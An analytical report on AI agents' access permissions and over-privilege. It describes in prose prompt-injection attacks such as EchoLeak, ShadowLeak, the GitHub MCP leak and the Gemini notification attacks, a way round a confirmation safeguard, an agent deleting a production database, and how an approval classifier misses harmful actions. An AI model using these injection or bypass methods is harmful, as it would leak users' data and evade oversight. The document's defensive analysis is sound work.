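# Access permissions and concentration of power in AI agents that use many tools

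## What access does an AI agent need, and how does it get it?

An AI agent is a system that uses a language model to choose and carry out actions in other software to reach a goal set by a user. A chatbot without access to other software can only list the steps, leaving the user to open the calendar, find the document and update the customer record (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*). An agent takes those steps itself, so it needs permission to access each system involved.

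Such permissions raise a security problem, because the permission that lets an agent send a report to a colleague usually lets it send anything to anyone. They also raise a problem of economic power, because the company that runs a mailbox or a phone decides which agents can access it and often sells an agent of its own.

### Agents, tools and connectors

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent's work as a loop. The user states a task in ordinary language. The model picks a tool, which is a function it can call to read data or to act, such as "search mail" or "send payment". The software around the model runs the tool and adds the result to the text the model reads, and the model then picks the next tool. A request to find mentions of an event in recent emails and save a summary might take a search, several retrievals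 and one write to a file. The developer of an ordinary phone app knows what the app does and can list its permissions at installation. No programmer fixes an agent's sequence of steps in advance, so the access it needs becomes known only with the task and can change partway through.

A connector is the link between an agent and one application, together with its tools and credentials. Many connectors now use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic introduced in 2024. The application's owner or a third party runs an MCP server that offers tools. The agent's software, known as the client, requests a list of these tools and then sends calls to the server. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a page of the specification, each tool has a name, a description and a schema for its inputs. A weather tool, for example, takes a city name or zip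 code. The model uses the descriptions to choose which tool to call. A server may list only the tools that the client's permissions allow.

The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) counted nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main development kits in July 2026. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports over 400 million, a fourfold rise within the year. Automated builds inflate download counts, so these figures show that developers have adopted the standard but are weak evidence of how many people use it.

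The Model Context Protocol (MCP) leaves much of the security to its adopters. *Authorization* (Model Context Protocol, 2026) makes authorisation optional, and MCP recommends but does not require that a person be able to refuse any tool call.

### Four ways in

Agents get access by four routes, and one task may use several. Each route gives the agent a different reach. An agent's reach is all the data and actions available to whoever holds its credentials.

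A consumer connector usually gets access through OAuth, the web's common standard for letting one application act in another on a user's behalf. The user's recorded consent, called a grant, covers the scopes they accepted, which are labels such as "view your email messages". Google ends a grant when the user revokes it, when the application has not used it for six months, or when the user changes their password and the grant includes Gmail, among other cases, so a connector used every week has no fixed end date. The user can revoke the grant in either application. For example, xAI points users of its assistant Grok to both Grok's connector page and the permissions page of their Google account.

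A stored key is a secret string that the agent's software keeps and presents like a password. MCP servers that run on the user's own machine typically use stored keys, since the specification has them take credentials from their environment instead of asking for consent. The key gives the agent whatever access its owner allowed when creating it. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes a coding assistant that connects to the code-hosting site GitHub with an older type of token. The assistant gets about 40 tools, 16 of which can make changes, and can use them in every repository the user can access. It needs only two read-only tools to summarise one repository's open issues.

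Companies also issue keys to service accounts, which belong to an application rather than a person, so no individual user has to consent. Anthropic lets a customer's administrators connect its workplace agent, Claude Tag, to Google data through a service account with "domain-wide delegation", a setting that allows the account to act for users across the organisation. Once saved, the first credential an administrator adds for a service works in every workspace and channel unless the administrator has already narrowed its scope. A stored key works until it expires, if it has an expiry date, or until the account's administrator deletes it, which an employee cannot do even if the service account can read their mailbox.

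The third route is the user's logged-in browser session. The agent controls a browser in which the user has already signed in, and the website treats its clicks as the user's. No scopes restrict the agent, so it can do whatever the user could do on that site, including changing settings or spending money. Limits are also hard to write because, as Christodorescu and colleagues point out, a browser agent acts through clicks and keystrokes, and a rule such as "comment but do not delete" has no clear meaning at that level. The session ends when it times out, usually after hours or days, or when the user signs out or the site ends it. Signing out does not affect OAuth grants that the user approved in the same browser. According to *Security Impact of GCP session length on OAuth clients* (2019), a grant's lifetime is separate from the session's once the user consents.

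The last route is operating-system permissions. On phones and computers, the user must turn on a setting before an app can read the screen, use the microphone, open files or simulate taps. An agent that can read the screen and simulate taps needs no cooperation from app developers. It can see whatever the user opens, including one-time login codes and messages from people who never agreed to that access. The permission generally lasts until the user turns it off, though some systems periodically prompt the user to renew it. An employer that manages the device can also withdraw it, and the maker of the operating system can withdraw it for every app at once. The maker's power to do this is why access to phone features has become a competition law issue.

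### One OAuth grant, step by step

Before OAuth, users who wanted an application to fetch their data from another service gave the application their password. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012) lists three problems with this arrangement. The application had to store the password, it got far more access than it needed, and users could shut it out only by changing the password, which also shut out every other application that used it. OAuth replaces the password with a separate credential for each application, so an employee can connect an agent to her mailbox without giving it her password.

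1. The agent's software sends her browser to the authorization server, the service that issues credentials for the mailbox. The request carries the agent's identifier, the scopes it wants and the address to which the browser should return.
2. The authorization server asks her to log in and shows a consent screen with the requested permissions. She types her password only here, so the agent never receives it. On Google's version she may grant some of the permissions and refuse others.
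3. If she agrees, the server sends her browser back to the agent's software with an authorization code. The code works once, and Hardt recommends a life of ten minutes at most.
4. The agent's software sends the code to the authorization server and receives an access token, usually with a refresh token. In Hardt's sample response the access token lasts 3,600 seconds, or one hour.
5. The software attaches the access token to each request, and the mail server checks it before answering. When the token expires, the software trades the refresh token for a new one. The employee sees nothing of this.

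A thief can use a stolen access token for an hour or so. A stolen refresh token works until the grant ends, though if the server requires the agent software's own credentials, the thief needs those too.

MCP adds two rules to this procedure. First, each token must name the server it is for, and a server must reject tokens meant for another. Second, when an agent tries something its token does not cover, the server replies with the missing scope so that the client can ask the user for it. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, the industry body that houses MCP, this "step-up" is needed because agents work for long periods and discover partway that they need further privileges, while earlier uses of OAuth were often designed for short interactions. The client requests the new scopes together with all those it requested before. This spares the user from granting the same thing twice, but it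 also means that the agent's access grows with each step-up.

### Least privilege, the confused deputy and prompt injection

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) set out the principle of least privilege, which says that every program and user should operate with the fewest privileges needed to complete the job. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an agent told to "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done". The agent should be able to open issue 745 on GitLab, a code-hosting site, and write in its comment box, but have no access to anything else in GitLab or the user's browser. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the right set of permissions changes. Google's *Requesting Minimum Scopes* applies the same principle to app developers, who must justify the scopes they request.

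A confused deputy is a program that is led to use its legitimate authority for someone who lacks that authority. Norm Hardy named the problem in 1988, citing a case involving a compiler, a program that translates source code. The compiler had permission to write to a system directory, where it recorded usage statistics. The same directory held the billing file. A user gave the compiler the billing file's name as the place to write its debugging output. The user had no permission to write there, but the compiler did, so it overwrote the billing data.

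An agent that a whole department shares can go wrong in the way Hardy described. In an article that a security vendor contributed to The Hacker News, an employee without permission to open certain data asks for it through an agent that has permission, and the access controls raise no alarm because the agent's credentials are valid. The vendor sells a remedy and does not say how often this happens.

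In a prompt injection, text that an agent reads while working makes it follow someone else's instructions. This works because the model receives the user's request and the fetched material as one body of text. In a case that Parkinson and colleagues cite, a malicious instruction in a public GitHub repository made an agent read its user's private repositories and publish what it found. The agent acted as a confused deputy, meaning that it used its user's access on behalf of whoever wrote the instruction.

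Telling an agent to ignore all instructions in what it reads would stop some useful work. For example, an agent summarising issue 745 may learn from the page that the issue depends on another one, and read that one too. Christodorescu and colleagues treat this as the same mechanism as prompt injection, and distinguish the two cases by who wrote the text and how far it changes the task. An agent often has no reliable way to check who wrote the text.

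Least privilege limits the damage a confused deputy can do, though it does not prevent the confusion. Parkinson and colleagues note that a token with read access to only the one public repository would have prevented the GitHub attack. They add that the user's next task might be to fix a failing build, which requires write access, and the one after that might involve a different repository. Whether a token's permissions can be adjusted for each task is a separate question.

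### An example: the sales brief

Suppose a sales employee asks an agent to prepare for a customer meeting by reading tomorrow's calendar entry, finding the latest mail thread with the customer, checking the customer's record and sending a one-page brief to a colleague. Mistral AI's *Google*, the documentation page for its Vibe assistant's Google connectors, lists the scopes that Vibe requests, and Google publishes what each Gmail scope allows. The comparison below shows how these scopes match what the task needs.

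| Step | What the task needs | What the connector receives |
|---|---|---|
| Read the calendar entry | Read one day of one calendar | Full calendar access: read, create, change and delete events |
| Find the mail thread | Search for one customer, read one thread | Read every message and the mail settings; change labels |
| Check the customer record | Read one record | Every record the employee may open (assumed) |
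| Send the brief | Send one message to one colleague | Manage drafts and send mail to anyone |

The row on the customer record is an assumption based on how other connectors work. Google's own MCP servers inherit the user's permissions, and Anthropic limits its Google connectors in the same way. This limit stops the agent from seeing anything the employee cannot see, but it still allows much more access than the task needs, because a salesperson may be able to open thousands of records and the brief concerns only one.

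Mistral has a reason for each scope. Vibe needs more than read-only calendar access, for instance, because it also creates and deletes events when users ask. The connector has to serve every task a user might bring, so Vibe gets the permissions for all of them even when it is only working on the sales brief. Google's scopes would not let Mistral limit access to what the brief needs anyway. Google offers a send-only mail scope, which is narrower than the one Vibe uses, but apart from a few scopes for Gmail add-ons, it offers none limited to one thread or one recipient.

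Mistral also requires the user to approve every action that changes something, such as sending a message, though users can approve specific actions in advance. This check is useful, but Mistral's software performs it, and it doesn't limit what the token permits. Mistral says it requests one of its Gmail scopes, `gmail.modify`, to organise labels, but Google defines that scope as also permitting reading, composing and sending mail. Anyone who obtained the token could do all of this without the user's approval.

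Other connectors can also request more access than a user needs. The forum post *How to Restrict OAuth Scopes for Gmail in n8n to Only gmail.send* describes a developer who needed the automation tool n8n only to send mail and manage a calendar, but Google detected that it was also requesting permission to read and modify the mailbox. Connectors also gain abilities over time. Claude's Gmail connector could at first only search and summarise mail, but it can now send, reply to and forward emails, according to Tom's Guide's *Claude can now send Gmail emails*.

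### Two meanings of concentration

"Concentration" can mean that much access sits in one place. The sales agent's provider may hold tokens for the employee's mail, calendar and customer records, and for those of many other customers, so one break-in or one misled agent could reach all of those accounts. It can also mean that a few firms hold most of a market. Either can occur without the other, since a company with a dozen staff can hold the tokens of hundreds of businesses, and a market of three large firms could in principle run on narrow tokens that expire within minutes.

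Access permissions and concentration of power are connected when one company controls access to a service, as Google does with Gmail. Google runs the mailbox and defines the scopes. It also requires verification and, according to Mistral's page for developers who bring their own app, an annual security assessment before an app with the more powerful Gmail scopes can serve anyone outside a test list of 100 users. The assessment protects people's mail, but every new maker of agents has to bear its cost. Google's MCP servers admit Anthropic's Claude alongside Google's own agent product, Antigravity, so Google both examines its rivals' agents and competes with them.

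## How does broad access turn into harm?

Broad access leads to harm in three ways. An outsider can use prompt injection to make the agent misuse its user's permissions. Permissions that are harmless separately can do damage when combined. The agent can also make a mistake when nobody is attacking it. The table lists the conditions for each kind of harm and the permission it can't happen without.

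| Route | Who acts | Preconditions | Steps | Fails without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Injected instructions | An outsider who can put text where the agent will read it | The agent reads outsiders' text during ordinary work and holds permissions they lack | The outsider sends the text; the user sets an ordinary task; the agent reads the text and obeys it | Permission for the action the outsider wants, such as reading private files |
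| Combined permissions | An outsider, an employee, or nobody with bad intentions | Someone approved each permission separately, and data can pass between the systems | The agent reads from one system and writes the content into another, where the wrong people can see it or act on it | Either of the two permissions |
| Agent error | The agent alone | The agent can use a credential that covers more than the task, and the system makes no further check | The agent chooses a wrong action; the system accepts it because the credential is valid | Permission for the damaging action |

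These routes overlap, since most injection attacks also exploit a combination of permissions, but they can require different remedies. For example, a filter that caught every malicious email would not stop an agent from deleting the wrong database by mistake.

### Injected instructions

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security found that a single email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, leak confidential data. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs the attack. The attacker needs only an employee's email address to send a message with hidden instructions. When the employee later asks Copilot an ordinary question about work, Copilot retrieves the message along with internal documents, follows the instructions, and writes an answer that includes an image's web address with confidential details in it. The employee's software loads the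 image automatically, which sends the details to the attacker.

The theft was possible because Copilot could read the emails and files that the employee could open. Copilot had no permission to send mail, but the data left through the feature that displays images in its answers. An administrator who looked only at Copilot's permissions would have seen no way for data to leave. Microsoft had restricted which sites the images could load from, but the researchers found a way around the restriction.

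Microsoft rated EchoLeak 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, a month before Aim Security published its findings. Aim Security had demonstrated the attack on a real product, but Microsoft reported no known use of it against customers. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case of its kind in a production system. That is doubtful, because *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) lists fourteen other cases of data theft that researchers had shown to be possible in commercial products, starting with ChatGPT in April 2023.

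A similar demonstration, ShadowLeak, used ChatGPT's Deep Research agent with a connected Gmail account. Hidden instructions in an email led the agent to search the inbox for sensitive data and then send it out by visiting a web address that contained it. The attack required both permission to read the mailbox and the ability to browse the web. As *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* points out, the web request came from the service's servers, so a company monitoring its employees' computers might not have detected it. The provider fixed the flaw in August 2025, about two months after receiving the report.

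Attackers can reach an agent without email if it reads a public website. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) details the GitHub attack described earlier, which worked this way. Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository. The researchers filed an issue containing instructions on their own demonstration repository. They then asked Claude Desktop, which they had connected to GitHub's MCP server, to look at the open issues. The leaked material appeared in a proposed change to the public repository and included the names of private projects, a fictional user's salary and the user's plan to move to South America.

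heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the agent had permission to read the private repositories because the server works with the user's whole account. The server's code had no bug, so Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem alone. Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, which might have stopped the attack. Invariant Labs says that many users choose "Always Allow" instead, but it gives no figures and sells security software for this problem.

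Injected instructions can also do harm without stealing anything. SafeBreach's *Gemini's Secret Affair* (2026) describes attacks by its researcher Or Yair, who sent messages to an Android phone whose owner used Google's Gemini voice assistant. Gemini could read the phone's notifications aloud, so anyone who could trigger a notification could get text to the model. In Yair's demonstrations, Gemini announced a fake message made to look like it came from a real contact, opened internet-connected windows, scheduled a daily reading of the user's recent messages, and saved a false name for the user in its long-term memory. Because that memory belongs to the Google account, the false name carried over to the user's other devices.

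Google already had a check meant to stop Gemini from taking such actions without the user's agreement. Yair got past it by making Gemini ask for confirmation in a way the user did not hear or could not understand, so that a "yes" to something harmless counted as consent. A confirmation step therefore protects users only if they know what they are confirming.

The messages reached Gemini through an Android permission called "Notification read, reply & control" (The Hacker News, 2026). Opening the windows also required Gemini's link to Google Home, which controls household devices. SafeBreach reported the flaw in August 2025, and Google confirmed in November that better text filtering had blocked the attack. The fix did not narrow the permission, so users who want to close this route must stop Gemini from reading notifications altogether. There is no evidence that anyone used the technique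 outside SafeBreach's tests. The most alarming demonstration, in which the phone joined a video call and began streaming, relied on a test phone that Yair had set up to send a trusted web address to his own server.

### The lethal trifecta

According to Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", an agent is vulnerable to data theft if it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out. He calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". An attacker can use the untrusted content to instruct the agent to send out the private data. Removing any one of the three elements blocks the theft, and Willison observes that vendors have usually fixed such flaws by removing the agent's way to send data out.

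The number of tools matters little in this test. GitHub's MCP server supplied all three elements by itself, since it could read strangers' issues, read private repositories and publish changes. A mail connector that can read and send also supplies all three, because anyone can write to the mailbox. Willison worries mainly that MCP encourages users to connect tools from different sources. A vendor can stop its own product from sending data out, but it can't anticipate every combination of tools that users assemble.

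The trifecta fits EchoLeak, ShadowLeak and the GitHub attack, provided that loading an image counts as a way to send data out. It does not fit the SafeBreach attack that opened windows, because the attacker neither needed nor received private data. It also does not cover deletion, such as an email persuading the sales agent to delete every appointment in next week's calendar. That attack requires only untrusted content and an agent with permission to change the calendar. Changing the bank details in a supplier's record would be worse, and it would not require a way to send data out either.

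Willison acknowledges in *New prompt injection papers* (2025) that the trifecta covers only data theft. He preferred a broader rule from Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), which allows an agent at most two of three properties in one session unless it is supervised by a person or another reliable check. The properties are processing untrustworthy inputs, having access to sensitive systems or private data, and being able to change state (alter something, such as a file or a setting) or communicate externally.

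Meta's rule covers most deletions, but it still lets an agent that handles untrustworthy inputs make changes, as long as it can't reach anything sensitive. Willison soon added a correction to *New prompt injection papers* saying that this combination can do harm even without private data. The rule therefore prevents the calendar attack only if the agent's developer classes a calendar as sensitive. Meta also states that the rule does not protect against agents' mistakes or excessive privileges.

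Both tests also flag many useful agents. The sales agent must read a customer's emails, which are private and come from an outsider, and it must send a message, so it has all three elements of the trifecta even with only the permissions the brief requires. Least privilege cannot remove the trifecta here, but it can sharply limit where the agent can send data, for instance by letting it write only to the one colleague.

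### Harmless permissions in combination

The trifecta is either present or absent, so it can't show how much unnecessary access an agent has. A rough measure is the number of paths along which data could travel. Suppose the sales employee has also connected the agent to a shared file store and the team's chat. The agent can now read four sources: the calendar, the mailbox, the customer records and the shared files. It also has five tools that send or write data, one each for emails, calendar invitations, customer records, shared files and chat posts. Anything it reads can go into anything it writes, so there are 4 × 5 = 20 paths. The brief needs only three of them, from the calendar, the mailbox and the customer record into one email.

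| What the agent can use | Paths | Needed for the brief | Unneeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| All 4 sources and all 5 tools | 20 | 3 | 17 |
| The same, without posting in the chat | 16 | 3 | 13 |
| All 5 tools, without reading shared files | 15 | 3 | 12 |
| All 4 sources, with email as the only tool | 4 | 3 | 1 |
| 3 sources, with email as the only tool | 3 | 3 | 0 |

Removing one tool removes four paths, one for each source. If that tool is email, the agent cannot send the brief, so the choice of tool matters. Adding a service that the agent can both read from and write to would raise the count from 20 to 30, since there would be five sources and six tools. The user would get ten new paths by approving one connection, and the consent screen would describe only the new service's own data.

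Some of the unneeded paths can cause harm without an attacker. For example, the agent might save the brief in a folder that the whole company can open, because earlier briefs are there. The employee is allowed to read the customer's record and to save files in that folder, so neither permission looks wrong, but together they let the agent expose the record to people who have no right to see it. Removing either permission would prevent this.

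The count is a rough guide because it treats all paths as equally dangerous. The three paths that the brief needs are among the riskiest, since the email tool can write to anyone. Limiting that tool to one recipient would make the agent much safer but leave the count at 20. The count also leaves out deletion, which moves no data, and ways for data to leave that aren't listed as tools, such as the image loading in EchoLeak. It covers only the agent's own tools, although another agent may read a file that this one saves.

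### Permissions spread over several agents

An organisation that runs many agents may give each one narrow permissions and still end up with a dangerous combination. In *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI*, Parisel (2026) argues that reviewing each agent's permissions separately cannot find such cases. He proposes "least autonomy" as an additional principle, under which an organisation also limits what its agents could do by influencing one another. His three-step method checks the design before anything goes wrong.

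The first step measures how far apart two resources are within the organisation. Parisel arranges the organisation as a tree, with the whole company at the top, then divisions, departments and teams, and individual resources such as a report or a signing key at the bottom. The distance between two different resources is

d = F / 2^(2D+1)

Here D is the depth of the smallest unit that contains both resources, with the whole company at depth 0. F is a multiplier between 1 and 2 that rises with the sensitivity of the more sensitive resource. Before applying F, two resources in the same team are 1/128 apart, in the same department 1/32, in different departments of one division 1/8, and in different divisions 1/2. Each level up the organisation multiplies the distance by four, while F can at most double it, so a pair that spans more of the organisation is always farther apart.

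In the second step, Parisel draws links between agents. Agent U has a link to agent V if U can write to something that V reads and the link's span is large enough. The span is the greatest distance between anything U can write and anything V can read, and the organisation sets the threshold for it. Agents that can message each other directly may also have a link, in both directions, because a reply can influence an agent as much as a request can. An agent's "effective autonomy" is its own permissions plus those of every agent it can reach through links.

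In the last step, the organisation looks for dangerous patterns among linked agents. An agent may approve access for another agent that it also influences, or it may influence whoever approves its requests. A group of linked agents may also have permissions covering two areas that the organisation wants to keep separate, such as payments and software releases. The organisation must also confirm that it meant to allow each link and that no agent's effective autonomy extends beyond a set limit.

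In Parisel's worked example, one agent requests the release of a resource in the finance department and writes evidence into a review queue. A second agent reads the queue and decides whether to grant the release. The requesting agent can also write a market-risk report in finance, and the deciding agent can also read a deployment policy in engineering. Those two documents are 1.75 × 1/8 = 0.21875 apart, which exactly meets the threshold, so the requesting agent has a link to the deciding agent. Each agent is well within the single-agent autonomy limit of 0.5, but the method still flags the pair because the requesting agent can shape the evidence behind the decision.

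Separate reviews of the two agents could easily miss this weakness. The formula does detect it, but partly by luck. If the deciding agent lost its permission to read the deployment policy, the greatest remaining distance would be 1.75 × 1/32, or about 0.055. That is below the threshold, so the link would disappear and the pair would pass, even though the first agent would still be writing the evidence for its own request. A lower threshold would catch the pair but would also flag many more links that may be harmless.

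Parisel acknowledges other limits. The method ignores timing and conditional approvals, and a flagged pair of agents is only a reason to look more closely, since the two may never act together. The results also depend on an accurate description of every resource and approval in the organisation. His example is invented, and he leaves testing how often the flags are right to future work. The distance measure treats reading a resource the same as deleting it, and the sensitivity labels do not cover whether data remains available.

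### Errors with no attacker

According to the AI Incident Database's *Railway API* page, a coding agent deleted PocketOS's production database, which held live customer data, in April 2026. PocketOS makes software that car-rental companies use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. The agent, Cursor running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, was working on a task in the company's staging environment, a separate copy of the system for testing. It used a broadly scoped token to delete the storage volume that contained the database at Railway, the company's hosting provider.

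In *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, PocketOS founder Jer Crane writes that an agent deleted the company's production data in nine seconds with a single request, which also removed the backups stored with the volume. Mahmoud Abdelwahab confirms the request on Railway's blog. The agent had found a token stored on the user's machine. Railway's software treated the agent's request like any other command with a valid token, so a thief with a copy of the token could have deleted the data too.

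This was possible because the token could delete production volumes, a permission that a task in the staging environment did not need. If the token had been limited to that environment, the mistake would have produced only an error message. One request could also destroy both the data and the nearby backups, which left the company dependent on its host to get the data back.

This incident harmed a business and its customers, unlike EchoLeak, ShadowLeak, the GitHub attack and SafeBreach's work on Gemini. Railway later recovered all the data, so the damage was the disruption to PocketOS and the rental companies. Crane blames both Cursor and Railway, and Railway has its own reputation to protect, but Crane and Railway agree on which request caused the deletion. A single case cannot show how often agents make such mistakes.

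Crane also reports that the agent, when asked to explain itself, listed the safety rules it had broken. Its answer is poor evidence of why it acted, since a language model can produce a plausible explanation for almost anything. Railway's software did not stop the request, and if the rules were in the agent's instructions, they did not stop it either.

The lethal trifecta does not apply here, because no outsider's text was involved. Meta's Rule of Two would not have prevented the deletion, because it allows an agent that reads only trustworthy material to access and change sensitive systems without supervision. One of Meta's examples is a coding agent with access to production systems and few human checks. The rule protects such an agent against strangers' instructions, but the agent can still delete the wrong thing.

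The PocketOS case also shows that a list of an agent's connectors can understate what the agent can access. The agent found the Railway token in the files on the user's machine. An agent that can read a developer's files can use any working credential stored in them, whether or not anyone meant it to.

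## Why do agents hold and use more access than their tasks need?

The token that PocketOS's agent used to delete the company's database allowed far more than the agent's task required. Agents often get excess access because they inherit accounts set up for people, and because the people who approve their requests approve too much. Models add to the risk by choosing powerful tools when weaker ones would do.

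### Accounts set up for people

A connector that inherits an employee's permissions also gets the ones the employee doesn't use. For Oso's *Least Privilege Research Report 2026* (2026), the security companies Oso and Cyera compared the permissions held by 2.4 million users of business applications with the permissions they used over 90 days. The users held 3.6 billion permissions, an average of 1,500 each, and used about 4% of them.

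Oso counts a permission as an action on a type of resource, such as "edit sales opportunities", so opening a single record counts as using the permission in full. In Oso's example, a sales manager with eight permissions views 15 of 500 opportunities and edits three. She has used two of her eight permissions (25%) but opened only 3% of the records. A misled agent with her account could copy all 500, so the 4% figure understates the excess in this respect. The figure may also overstate the excess, because some people need a permission only once a year or in an emergency.

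Cyera's *96% of Enterprise Permissions Go Unused* (2026) reports that in most applications, only 4% of workers did anything during a 90-day period, and those workers used 17% of their permissions. These figures are hard to reconcile with the 96% in the title. If active and inactive workers held similar numbers of permissions, less than 1% of all permissions would have been used. The 17% figure is probably more useful for agents, since people are likely to connect an agent to applications they actually use. An agent with a typical active user's account would have about six times as many permissions as that user exercises.

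Much of the excess comes from the way companies hand out access. According to Cyera, more than 80% of it comes through fixed profiles, which administrators set up once and then expand as roles grow. Some companies had made nearly 30% of users administrators, when the recommended share is 2–5%. In Salesforce, a customer database, a permission called "Modify All Data" lets its holder read, change and delete every record. If the sales employee had that permission, an agent that inherited her account could delete the company's whole customer list while preparing her brief.

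Oso sells software that limits agents' permissions and Cyera sells data security, so both benefit from an alarming result. Their data came from organisations that already invest in access security. In Oso's *The 96% Blind Spot* (2026), the company's chief executive infers that the gap is almost certainly worse at other organisations, which is plausible but untested.

Microsoft (2021) also found, in risk assessments at more than 150 organisations, that over 90% of cloud identities used less than 5% of their permissions. This finding predates Oso's study, which Oso calls the first empirical measurement of how companies use access. Parkinson and colleagues cite an academic study from 2022 in which 99.8% of 447,000 automated GitHub workflows had more privileges than they needed. Those workflows are programs, so giving agents their own accounts would not be enough to prevent excess access.

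It is less clear how many agents inherit employees' access. Oso cites research by CyberArk, another security company, in which 45% of enterprises applied the same privileged access controls to AI agents as to people. But a company could apply the same controls and still give each agent a separate account with narrow access.

### What people agree to share

People also give agents access through consent screens and approval prompts. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues tested how well people make these decisions. They asked 205 adults in the United States to imagine training a personal assistant. Each participant answered 20 questions about sharing data for tasks in areas such as travel, health and finance. For each item of data, participants could choose to share it always, share it once, refuse it once or never share it. In five of the questions,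 the agent also asked for data that the task did not need.

At least once, 97% of participants overshared, meaning they released data the task did not require, and 91.1% withheld data it did require. Nobody got every decision right, and only 18.7% chose correctly for at least nine in ten items. Participants seemed to judge how sensitive an item was more readily than whether the task needed it. They overshared the name of their workspace in 88.9% of cases, but wrongly withheld their US Social Security number in about 46%.

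Wu and colleagues also asked participants which data a task needed. Participants shared 78.2% of the items they wrongly believed were necessary. Wu and colleagues think this suggests that many users believe an agent even when it is wrong. But participants also shared about 38% of the items they had correctly identified as unnecessary, so explaining what a task needs would not stop all oversharing.

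People were more careful when the agent mistakenly asked for unnecessary data alongside the necessary data. The proportion of participants who chose "always share" at least once fell from 82.8% to 74.4%, and the proportion who chose "never share" at least once rose from 68% to 78.8%.

These results may not match behaviour with a real agent. The researchers asked participants about their privacy concerns at the start and warned them that the agent might request too much, which probably made them more cautious than usual. On the other hand, the scenarios were imaginary, so oversharing had no real consequences for them.

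Constant permission prompts would defeat the purpose of an agent, so Wu and colleagues built a program to predict each user's answers. It gives a language model the user's past decisions and predictions based on similar users' decisions. The program matched the user's choice 85.1% of the time. When it answered only the requests it was confident about, its accuracy rose to 94.4%, but it left about three-quarters of the requests to the user. With no past decisions to learn from, its accuracy was 66.9%.

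When it answered every request, the program approved 15.2% of those that users had refused. Even a perfect predictor would copy the user's choices, including the oversharing. Wu and colleagues measured whether the program agreed with the user, not whether the task needed the data.

### Do users read approval prompts?

Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, originally asked users to approve each command or file change by default. Parkinson and colleagues cite Anthropic's figure that users approved 93% of these prompts, which comes from a March 2026 engineering post, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. Anthropic mentions the figure in passing while discussing "approval fatigue", in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve, and does not say how many users or prompts it covers. In August 2026, Anthropic reported a rate of 97% in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*.

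A high approval rate does not prove fatigue, because a perfectly attentive user would also approve 97% of commands if 97% were harmless. Anthropic points out that users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code proposes, which suggests they read plans more closely than commands. But users may reject a plan because they prefer another design, so the comparison is weak evidence about whether they would notice a dangerous command.

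Anthropic's better evidence comes from an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the text of one approval prompt changed to show a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more prompts, a drop consistent with approval fatigue.

The testers worked in a test environment, where mistakes could not damage their own projects, so they may have been less careful than usual. Their attention may also have declined because they wanted to finish a paid task. The result is still much stronger evidence than the 93% figure, because it measures how often people miss something they should have refused.

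Many users also avoid the prompts. By June 2026, nearly half of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that approved some commands in advance. Most of these rules were very broad. Some allowed any Python program, for example, which in practice lets the agent run almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with approval prompts switched off. Requiring more approvals can therefore backfire, because users may respond by giving the agent a broad standing permission.

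### Automated approval

Anthropic's response was auto mode, in which software approves or blocks actions in place of the user. It works as follows.

1. Actions that cannot change anything, such as reading a file, go ahead without further checks. So do edits inside the project folder. The user's narrow approval rules still apply, but auto mode sets aside rules broad enough to let the agent run any code.
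2. A second model, called the classifier, reviews the remaining actions. It sees the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions, but not the agent's explanations or the material the agent has read. This makes it harder for the agent, or for text planted on a web page, to persuade the classifier.
3. The classifier first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, it reasons through the case before making a final decision.
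4. If the classifier blocks the action, the agent looks for a safer way to continue. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the user has to step in.

A separate check scans the material that the agent reads and warns it about text that looks like a prompt injection.

The classifier's second look greatly reduces unnecessary interruptions but lets more harmful actions through. In Anthropic's March tests, it cut the share of ordinary actions wrongly blocked from 8.5% to 0.4%. But in a test on 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond what the user authorised, the quick check missed 6.6% and the full process missed 17%. With so few cases, the full process's true miss rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%.

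In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who asks the agent to "clean up" a proposed code change has not necessarily agreed to let it overwrite the project's history. The classifier has to infer consent from a short request that does not list the steps.

Anthropic accepts that auto mode may be worse than a person who reviews every action carefully, and it recommends manual review for high-stakes changes to production systems. But it argues that most people do not review carefully. In the experiment with paid testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. It stopped 800 that the testers had approved and allowed only six that the testers stopped.

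Other evidence for auto mode is weaker. Among real sessions flagged by Anthropic's safety systems, 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode contained a seriously harmful action that the user had not explicitly requested. But Anthropic did not assign users to a mode at random, so the difference may come from the users or their tasks. The harm ratings also came from a model. In a prompt injection test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 attempts succeeded against Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% succeeded with approval checks switched off, so these attacks were too weak to show how much protection auto mode adds.

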